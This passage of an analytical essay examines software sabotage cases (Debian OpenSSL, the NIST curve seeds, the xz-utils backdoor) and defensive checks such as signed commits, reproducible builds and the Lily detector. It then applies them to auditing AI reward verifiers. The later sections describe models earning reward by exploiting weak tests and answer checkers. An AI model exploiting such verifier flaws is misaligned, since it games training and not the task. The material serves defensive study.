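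A denial proves little, because a saboteur could say the same thing as an honest programmer. Many people suspected that security services were behind Heartbleed, a serious flaw in the encryption software OpenSSL. nk497's *Heartbleed Coder* reports that Robin Seggelmann, who wrote the flawed code, told a newspaper he had forgotten to check a value containing a length, and that the reviewer had missed the error too. The part about the reviewer is more useful because others can check it, although a reviewer would also miss a well-disguised flaw.

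People may be evasive about an honest mistake because they are embarrassed. The Minnesota researchers, posting as "James Bond", apologised politely for a flaw they had planted.

### The Debian flaw of 2006

OpenSSL makes secret keys from random numbers, and its random number generator needs a starting value that nobody can guess. In 2006 a Debian maintainer, Kurt Roeckx, disabled two lines of code that supplied nearly all the unpredictable input. This left only 32,767 possible starting values, so an attacker could generate and try every possible key of a given type and size. The flaw lasted until May 2008, when users had to install a fix and replace their weak keys.

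CITP's *The Debian OpenSSL Bug* concludes that the flaw was probably a mistake. It would have been ideal for a spy, and some people suspected that one was responsible.

The change had a genuine purpose. Valgrind, which later reported errors in xz-utils, had flagged the two lines. *Debian, OpenSSL, and a lack of cooperation* (Edge, 2008) traces the problem to a user's report that April. A commenter at CITP had received the same warning a few years earlier, but investigated it and left the lines alone. Roeckx had also discussed the idea in public and asked a colleague's opinion before making the change.

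There was also good evidence that he was a real person. Another commenter pointed out that many developers had signed his digital key, which they do after meeting the owner face to face, and that some had signed it twice, years apart. An invented contributor like Jia Tan would struggle to get those signatures.

Debian later made Roeckx its Secretary, which CITP also counts in his favour. A commenter suggested, perhaps jokingly, that a secret organisation might have been pushing him up the ranks. The promotion is weak evidence either way, because a capable infiltrator might be about as likely to win it as an honest developer.

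Another commenter made the better objection that Roeckx knew roughly what the lines were for, since he had written that they added numbers to the pool used for randomness. But he wrote this in a public message asking for advice, which would have been a risky way to prepare sabotage.

None of this proves the flaw was accidental. Schneier and colleagues write that they would call the flaw plausibly deniable if someone had planned it, because an honest engineer without expertise in cryptography could have made the same change. Schneier had already observed in *Random Number Bug in Debian Linux* (2008) that such flaws are easy to create by accident and hard to discover later.

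### The elliptic-curve seeds

The Debian flaw was real, so people argued only about intent. People suspected sabotage in the US elliptic curves for years, although nobody had found a flaw in them.

An elliptic curve is a type of equation that many encryption and digital signature systems rely on. NIST published a set of them in 2000. Cook (2026), in *Cloud of suspicion lifted from NIST curves*, gives their form as

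y² = x³ − 3x + b (mod p)

where p is a large prime number and "mod p" means keeping only the remainder after dividing by p. As far as anyone knows, nearly every value of b is secure. But someone might secretly know of a rare weak value.

The designers computed each b by putting an arbitrary number, called a "seed", through a scrambling function called a hash. This made it impractical to pick a weak b and work backwards to a seed, but someone could have kept trying seeds until one produced a weak b. The NSA had supplied the seeds "with no explanation or justification", according to Anthropic's *Claude reveals ECDSA curve origins* (2026).

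The suspicion was reasonable, and Cook states plainly that the NSA did put a backdoor in Dual EC. In 2014 the cryptographer Daniel Bernstein asked Jerry Solinas of the NSA about the seeds. Solinas said they came from hashing a humorous English message that he no longer remembered. In 2023 the cryptographer Filippo Valsorda offered a bounty for recovering the message.

In October 2026, researchers at Anthropic, using its Claude model, found that the seeds came from an ordinary random number generator started from the computer's clock, not from a message. A program generated one candidate after another and discarded those that gave unsuitable curves. For the widely used curve P-256, the clock read 01:52:34 UTC on 16 August 1997, and the 1,842nd candidate became the published seed. Valsorda wrote a separate version of the program and confirmed the result (*The NIST Elliptic Curves Seeds Bounty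 Has Been Claimed*, 2026).

This evidence didn't depend on trusting anyone at the NSA. Valsorda calculated how many options a dishonest employee could have had. Picking any of the roughly 63 million seconds in 1997 and 1998, and then any of the first 16 suitable candidates, would give only about a billion options, or 2³⁰. Bernstein and Tanja Lange had described a way to plant a weak curve that could have used 2⁷⁰ options, more than a trillion times as many. Valsorda says the discovery completely rules out their method.

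Two oddities would have looked bad to a suspicious investigator. Solinas's account was wrong, apparently because his memory had faded, and the program produces about twice as many suitable seeds as the NSA published. For P-256, it had already accepted the 876th candidate, and nobody knows why it was skipped. Valsorda suggests that there may have been a bug, or that another part of the program was using up some of the random numbers.

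### Wrongly accusing and wrongly excusing

Cook says that suspicion held back adoption of the curves, and Valsorda says the speculation harmed confidence in sound systems. Valsorda now recommends the curves over Bernstein's competing design. But newer signature methods, meant to withstand quantum computers, are about to replace them.

Suspicion also falls on people. On the day Freund reported the xz-utils backdoor, someone replying on the same mailing list asked for extra scrutiny of Linux patches that Collin had recently sent. That was sensible, because Jia Tan had been involved in the patches to some degree and the code could be checked again without accusing anyone. GitHub did more harm by suspending Collin's account. Two days after Freund's report, Velvindron was asking for the account to be restored while Collin worked through Jia Tan's commits. At Minnesota, suspicion led to a ban on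 honest contributors and a review that found no sabotage in 435 commits.

Assuming that every flaw is a mistake also has a drawback. In the example of 100,000 verifiers, the assumption would be correct for about 99.65% of the flawed ones but would miss all 100 sabotaged ones. If staff record each flaw as a separate bug, they may never notice that several came from the same person.

A 26% probability is far too low to call someone a saboteur, but high enough to justify reading that person's other changes and asking a colleague to approve new ones until the matter is clearer. This would take some of an innocent author's time and might embarrass them, so it would help to treat these checks as routine after any serious flaw.

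*Lessons from the Debian/OpenSSL Fiasco* argues that, because everyone makes mistakes, who made this one is less interesting than the situation that encouraged it and let it go unnoticed for almost two years. Focusing on the situation is a good way to prevent the next accident, and it spares the programmer a public accusation. It works less well if the programmer introduced the flaw on purpose, because they may still have permission to change the code.

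## Which checks work without knowing intent?

A saboteur whose flaw passes for a mistake may keep permission to change the code, but gains little if someone finds the flaw before it does any harm. Checks that compare, rebuild or test code give the same result whether its author was careless or malicious. Each catches only some kinds of change:

| Check | Linux, 2003 | Minnesota, 2020 | xz-utils, 2024 |
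|---|---|---|---|
| Comparing independent copies | Yes, this is how it came to light | No, the patches arrived by the normal route | No, the copies would have matched |
| Requiring signed commits | Yes, the intruder had no key for the borrowed name | No, a newcomer can have a key too | No, Jia Tan could sign |
| Reproducible builds | No, they start from whatever source they get | No, for the same reason | No, the official tarball was already altered |
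| Comparing releases with source | No, the change wasn't in a release | No, release and source would have matched | Yes, the altered script was only in the tarball |
| A second reviewer | No, the intruder bypassed review | Perhaps, since reviewers recognised one flaw in three | Perhaps, if the reviewer had questioned the test files |

Comparing copies is cheap. As BitMover's nightly checksums showed in 2003, it needs little more than an original that the attacker can't reach.

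### Signed commits

Git lets developers enter any name and email address, so the name on a commit doesn't prove who made it. A digital signature ties the commit to a private key. The developer's computer calculates a short number from the change, its message and the names attached to it, then signs that number with the key. Anyone with the matching public key can check the signature.

Few developers sign their commits. *Attributing Open-Source Contributions is Critical but Difficult* (Holtgrave, Friedrich and colleagues, presented at the NDSS security conference in 2025) examined 50,328 widely used projects on GitHub. Of the people who had committed changes, 95.4% had never signed a commit and only 2.0% had signed all of theirs. In 72.1% of the projects, nobody had ever signed a commit.

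The study's summary also says that attackers could abuse the contribution process in 85.9% of the projects, but this figure is based on 7,546 projects, not all 50,328, because GitHub provides only recent records of who uploaded which commits. In 6,479 of the 7,546, at least one commit was uploaded by an account other than the one named as its author or committer. A false name is harder to notice in such a project. But automated accounts and ordinary code review cause the same mismatch, so the figure is an upper limit on how many projects are at risk and doesn't measure actual abuse.

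The main difficulty with signing is managing the keys. GitHub could confirm only 82% of the signatures developers made with PGP, the most common method. When it couldn't confirm one, the usual reason was that it didn't have the public key. A project that rejected every unconfirmed signature would turn away a lot of honest work.

A valid signature also doesn't show who holds the key. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* suggests asking for legal proof of identity before a contributor becomes a maintainer, which would have been a serious obstacle for Jia Tan. But attackers can steal digital identities, and developers of privacy tools may have good reasons to hide their names from governments.

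### Does the package match the source?

A build is reproducible if anyone who compiles the same source in the same way gets an identical file. If a distributor's file differs from the one that independent builders get, something changed during the build. Comparing the files could expose an attack like the one on the software company SolarWinds, in which intruders altered source code while it was being built. Builders also have to record the tools they used, and *What's missing to have reproducible builds on PyPI* (Cannon, 2026) points out that this makes it easier to find software built with a tool that later proves to be compromised. As of August 2026, PyPI, the main public collection of Python packages, had no defined way to record them.

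A build date stored in the file is enough to make two builds differ. *Does Functional Package Management Enable Reproducible Builds at Scale?* (2025) examined packages from the Nix software collection between 2017 and 2023. The share that were reproducible ranged from 69% to 91% over that period, and build dates caused about 15% of the failures.

In May 2026, Debian made reproducibility a condition for packages to enter or stay in "testing", the version that becomes its next release, according to *Reproductibilité obligatoire, tests de paquets binaires et nouvelle architecture* (Sibaud, 2026). Among packages that don't depend on the type of processor, 23,371 passed and 414 failed.

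The xz-utils backdoor could have passed a reproducible-build check, because independent builders who made Debian packages from the official tarball would all have got the same backdoored library.

Comparing the tarball with the repository would have worked better. GitHub automatically creates an archive of the repository for each release, but xz-utils releases also included four archives that a maintainer uploaded by hand, and only these contained the altered script. But packaging normally adds files, so a simple comparison shows many harmless differences. Someone has to regenerate those files and compare the results, much as Collin did when he made his own tarball of version 5.4.5.

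Distributors can also compare the compiled versions of two releases. *Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models* (2025) had language models summarise the differences between the compiled libraries of xz 5.4.7 and 5.6.0, then judge whether the changes were malicious. GPT-5 correctly judged them malicious. The smaller GPT-5 mini called them benign when it worked from its own summaries, but malicious when it worked from GPT-5's. This is weak evidence that the method would catch unknown backdoors, because the models' training data may have covered the xz-utils backdoor.

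A simpler approach is to watch which files each stage of a build opens. *Build Code is Still Code* describes Foreman, a prototype with only 177 lines of Python. Its developers wrote a rule that the compiling stage must not open test files. When they built the compromised xz-utils, Foreman flagged exactly the two files that held the payload, without needing to analyze their contents. But people have to write these rules by hand, and Foreman's developers already knew where the payload was. Applying the rule to the configuration stage as well would have produced dozens of false alarms, because that stage has legitimate reasons to open test files.

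### A second reviewer

GitHub can block a change until someone other than its author approves it. This rule would have stopped Jia Tan from adding the payload alone. But Collin was the obvious second reviewer, and he might have accepted two more unreadable test files from a colleague he had worked with for two years.

How useful an approval is depends on how carefully the reviewer read the change. When Jia Tan asked Google's OSS-Fuzz service to stop testing one feature of xz-utils, a program labelled the request "ready to merge" because Jia Tan was a listed contact for the project and had contributed to it before. The request was approved quickly. A Google engineer later explained that developers decide which parts of their projects the service tests.

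In Wu and Lu's baseline, reviewers caught 56.6% of the use-after-free flaws. As a rough estimate, adding a second reviewer who independently caught the same share would raise this to about 81% (1 − 0.434²). For flaws involving concurrency, the share caught would rise from 19.4% to about 35%. The gain would be smaller in practice, because a flaw that one reviewer misses is probably hard for the next one too.

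These checks take time, which a project like xz-utils didn't have. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* therefore recommends paying maintainers, who could then review more and would have less need to hand sensitive tasks to people they don't know well.

### Lily: behaviour that is both new and unusual

In October 2026, Kokkonis and colleagues presented Lily, their backdoor detector that watches system calls. It tests a program by running it, so it doesn't depend on anyone reading the code correctly. It works in four steps:

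1. Lily runs the new version of a program on inputs saved from tests of earlier versions. For each input, it records which types of system call the program makes. These combinations count as normal.
2. A fuzzer then spends ten minutes generating new inputs, keeping those that reach code no earlier input had reached.
3. If one of these inputs produces a combination of system calls that isn't on the normal list, Lily tries the same input on the old version.
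4. If the old version doesn't produce that combination, Lily raises an alarm and points to the changed lines responsible.

In the tampered version of vsFTPd, for example, the fuzzer eventually produced a user name containing a smiley face. The program responded with system calls that never occurred together on the saved inputs, and the old version didn't respond that way. Lily's report highlighted seven lines, whereas a reviewer comparing the two versions would have had to read 1,407.

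The researchers tried Lily on 482 harmless changes (432 commits and 50 releases) and 63 with a backdoor (13 commits and 50 releases). They ran each test 20 times because fuzzing involves chance.

| | Commits | Releases |
|---|---|---|
| Runs that detected the backdoor | 233 of 260 (90%) | 828 of 1,000 (83%) |
| False alarms with both conditions | 17 of 8,640 (0.2%) | 43 of 1,000 (4.3%) |
| False alarms if new behaviour were enough | 10% | 58% |
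| False alarms if unusual behaviour were enough | 14% | 20% |

Combining the two conditions makes Lily practical, because legitimate updates often add new behaviour and legitimate programs often do unusual things. Of the 43 false alarms on releases, 40 came from two updates to the same sound library.

Even a false-alarm rate of 0.2% produces many more false alarms than real ones if backdoors are rare. If one commit in 100,000 contained a backdoor, Lily would raise about 200 false alarms for each backdoor. An alarm would therefore be a very poor basis for accusing anyone, but it only requires a maintainer to read about a dozen lines.

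Lily detected every backdoor in at least one of the 20 runs, but a single run can miss one. For releases of the image library libpng, it succeeded in only 31 of 80 runs. Three of the 13 backdoors came from real attacks, and the other ten were synthetic, from a collection the researchers had built. On average, the fuzzer reached only about 32% of the changed code, mostly because of limitations in the small programs that feed it inputs. Lily checks only new changes, so a project needs a separate audit to find backdoors it already has.

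Lily probably wouldn't have helped in the three main cases. The 2003 lines of code were in the kernel, which answers system calls from other programs, while Lily monitors the calls an ordinary program makes. The Minnesota flaws were memory errors, which other fuzzing tools look for. The researchers didn't test Lily on xz-utils, where the backdoor appeared only in certain package builds.

### Recording which reward code ran

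Laboratories can use the same methods to control who changes reward code. They can require signatures and a second approval, and store a checksum of the verifier, tests, answer key and settings used in each training run. If the checksum at the start of a run doesn't match that of the approved version, someone has changed a file since it was approved. This check also works for packages from outside suppliers.

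A routine comparison might also have found the altered code that the ByteDance intern's former colleagues described sooner, provided it covered the affected files.

A matching checksum shows only that the approved code ran. If the approved tolerance is wrong, every copy will have the same error, so someone also has to test the verifier's verdicts.

### Trying answers that are known to be wrong

The most direct test is to give the verifier wrong answers and see whether it accepts them. In the earlier example of a program that finds the largest number in a list, accepting even one program that handles only positive numbers would show that the tests are too weak.

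To get wrong answers, Zhang had the model itself write 16 programs for each task before training, then ran them on the ordinary tests, about three per task, and on a much larger set. A task's "leakiness" is the share of programs passing the ordinary tests that fail the larger set. If ten programs pass the ordinary tests and two of those fail the larger set, the leakiness is 0.2.

The audit was good at predicting which tasks' ordinary tests would later reward failing programs. Its rank correlation was 0.80, where 1 would mean that it had put the tasks in exactly the right order. On tasks the audit had flagged, 45.9% of the rewarded programs failed the larger set of tests, compared with 2.1% on the others. About half of these failing programs came from 18 of the 250 tasks, so a laboratory with little time could repair those tasks' tests first. For two other models, the correlations were 0.81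 and 0.70.

Zhang then trained one group of models with the ordinary tests and another with the larger set. The group trained with the ordinary tests earned 8.37 points more reward during training, but this didn't reflect greater ability. On tasks that neither group had trained on, the models trained with the larger set scored 0.20 points higher, with a 90% interval from 0.42 points lower to 0.74 higher. The larger set made the reward more accurate but barely improved the models. The models were small, with 1 to 1.5 billion parameters, and the tasks were short, so weak tests could do more harm with larger models or longer tasks.

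The audit can miss weak tests when few programs pass. If only four programs pass the ordinary tests and all four also pass the larger set, the true leakiness could still be as high as 60%. Programs written during training later exposed weak tests on 74 tasks that had looked clean, which is a good reason to repeat the audit as the model changes.

The larger set was imperfect too. Zhang checked all 2,821 rewarded programs that had failed it in the first model's runs and confirmed that about 48% were really wrong. Others had failed because of faulty tests, invalid inputs or time limits. The first estimate had been 69%, and it fell as Zhang ruled out more of these causes. Somebody therefore has to review the cases where the verifier and the larger set disagree before blaming the verifier, let alone its author.

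### Fuzzing a verifier

A model can take a while to write a mistake that exposes a flaw in the verifier, so Ray generated wrong answers automatically, for example by adding a second, contradictory answer or leaving out part of the original. Ray then ran a deliberately faulty verifier and a stricter one on each response. Responses that only the faulty verifier accepted were likely false positives to examine.

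The faulty verifiers accepted 83.2% of the wrong answers in mathematics, 86.9% in tasks where a model sends instructions to another program, and 55.7% in programming. The stricter ones accepted none of the same answers. Ray also added the improvements one at a time, to find out which of them mattered. These are the results for mathematics:

| Rule in the verifier | Wrong answers accepted, out of 120 |
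|---|---|
| Accept the first number anywhere in the response | 100 |
| Also require a marked final answer | 28 |
| Also reject contradictory final answers | 28 |
| Also require a close numerical match | 0 |

The third rule made no difference once the second was in place, though it looks sensible. A reviewer can also use such a comparison to see what would happen if somebody removed a rule, whatever their stated reason.

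These tests need no training run or specialised processor, so they are easy to repeat after every change to the verifier. It is better to run them before training, because some faults are very easy to find. A simple search with access only to the rewards found an exploitable mathematics answer within two attempts in 94 of 100 trials, and within four attempts in all of them.

But Ray planted the faults and wrote the stricter verifiers to remove them, so scores of zero don't show that the method would find every fault in someone else's code. The fuzzer can find only the kinds of error it tries, so it would miss the off-by-one fault that Xin found if it never used a reference answer of 10,000 or more. Ray also didn't test the method on a full training run of a language model.

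### Scoring with a separately written verifier

A second verifier can be useful even if nobody knows which of the two is right. If they disagree, at least one is wrong or the task's rules are unclear.

Ray tried this with existing open-source checkers. On 100 mathematics responses, math-verify accepted all 40 right answers and ten of the 60 wrong ones. Another checker, based on the algebra program SymPy, accepted the same 40 right answers and no wrong ones. The ten responses on which the checkers differed all mentioned the correct value without marking it as the final answer, so whether they deserved a reward depends on the task's requirements.

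Ray presents this as a trade-off because the SymPy checker accepted fewer responses overall, but on this sample the extra responses it rejected were all wrong. It could read only 76 of the 100 responses, compared with 90 for math-verify. A third checker, for structured data, rejected all 80 wrong responses it received because it couldn't read any of them, so it would have looked perfect in a report that gave only the false-positive rate.

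This check can take a lot of work when there are many disagreements. In Xin's audit, two settings of the same library gave different results on 49.9% of the answers, so staff would have to group the disagreements by cause or read a sample.

Two verifiers can also make the same mistake, especially if they share an answer key or the same person wrote both. A language model can be unreliable as the second scorer. In one of Zhang's side experiments, DeepSeek-V4-Pro read programs without running them and tried to tell the wrongly rewarded ones from the correct ones. On a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect, it scored 0.89 on programs from a small model but only 0.62 on its own. A different company's model did about as badly on DeepSeek's programs, so favouritism probably wasn't the reason. The stronger model's mistakes may have been harder to see. Separately written tests that run the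 programs wouldn't rely on that kind of judgement.

The second verifier can score a sample of answers in the background without affecting training, so the policy receives no reward for satisfying it. A growing gap between the two verifiers' scores would be a reason for staff to start reading answers. Arunkumar and colleagues could also predict the kind of failure by auditing a verifier before training.

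### What to keep when someone finds a flaw

Staff who find a faulty verifier will want to correct it and restart the training run. If they overwrite the old files, they may never learn where the fault came from or which models it affected.

Ray's system records every verdict, including the task, the response, the answer the verifier extracted, the reward, and the verifier's name and version. Somebody can use such a record to trace an undeserved reward to the code that gave it.

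Zhang's experiment shows how missing records limit later checks. For the first of the three models, Zhang had kept neither the individual answers from the final tests nor the finished models. Performance on tasks with weak tests seemed to have improved less, but Zhang couldn't establish whether the tests were the cause. Zhang later wanted to score the final answers under a stricter rule, but could do so only for the other two models.

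After finding a flaw, a laboratory should keep at least:

- the faulty version exactly as it ran, with its tests, answer key and settings
- the record of who wrote and approved the change, when, and what explanation they gave
- a list of every training run, evaluation and data collection that used that version
- the models' answers and rewards, and saved copies of the models from before and after the fault took effect

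The people who write the reward code shouldn't be able to alter these records. In 2003, the false log entries were on the machine the intruder had broken into, so even their timestamps are doubtful. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* recommends public logs that list every published file. Anyone could then check that a file is listed, and a developer could notice a release someone else made with a stolen key. A laboratory could keep a similar internal log of its verifiers.

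If staff saved the old answers, they can rescore them with the corrected verifier. Suppose a run rewarded 50,000 answers and the corrected verifier rejects 4,400 of them. If most of the rejected answers come from a few tasks, those tasks probably had weak tests. If all the rejected answers contain the same phrase, the policy may have learned to produce it.

If the phrase became more common across the copies of the model saved during training, the reward probably encouraged it. In Zhang's runs, false positives didn't become more common. The untrained models already made most of the same characteristic mistakes, so the weak tests had mainly failed to correct them.

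Staff also need to run the same check on any model that started from a saved copy of the affected one or trained on its answers.
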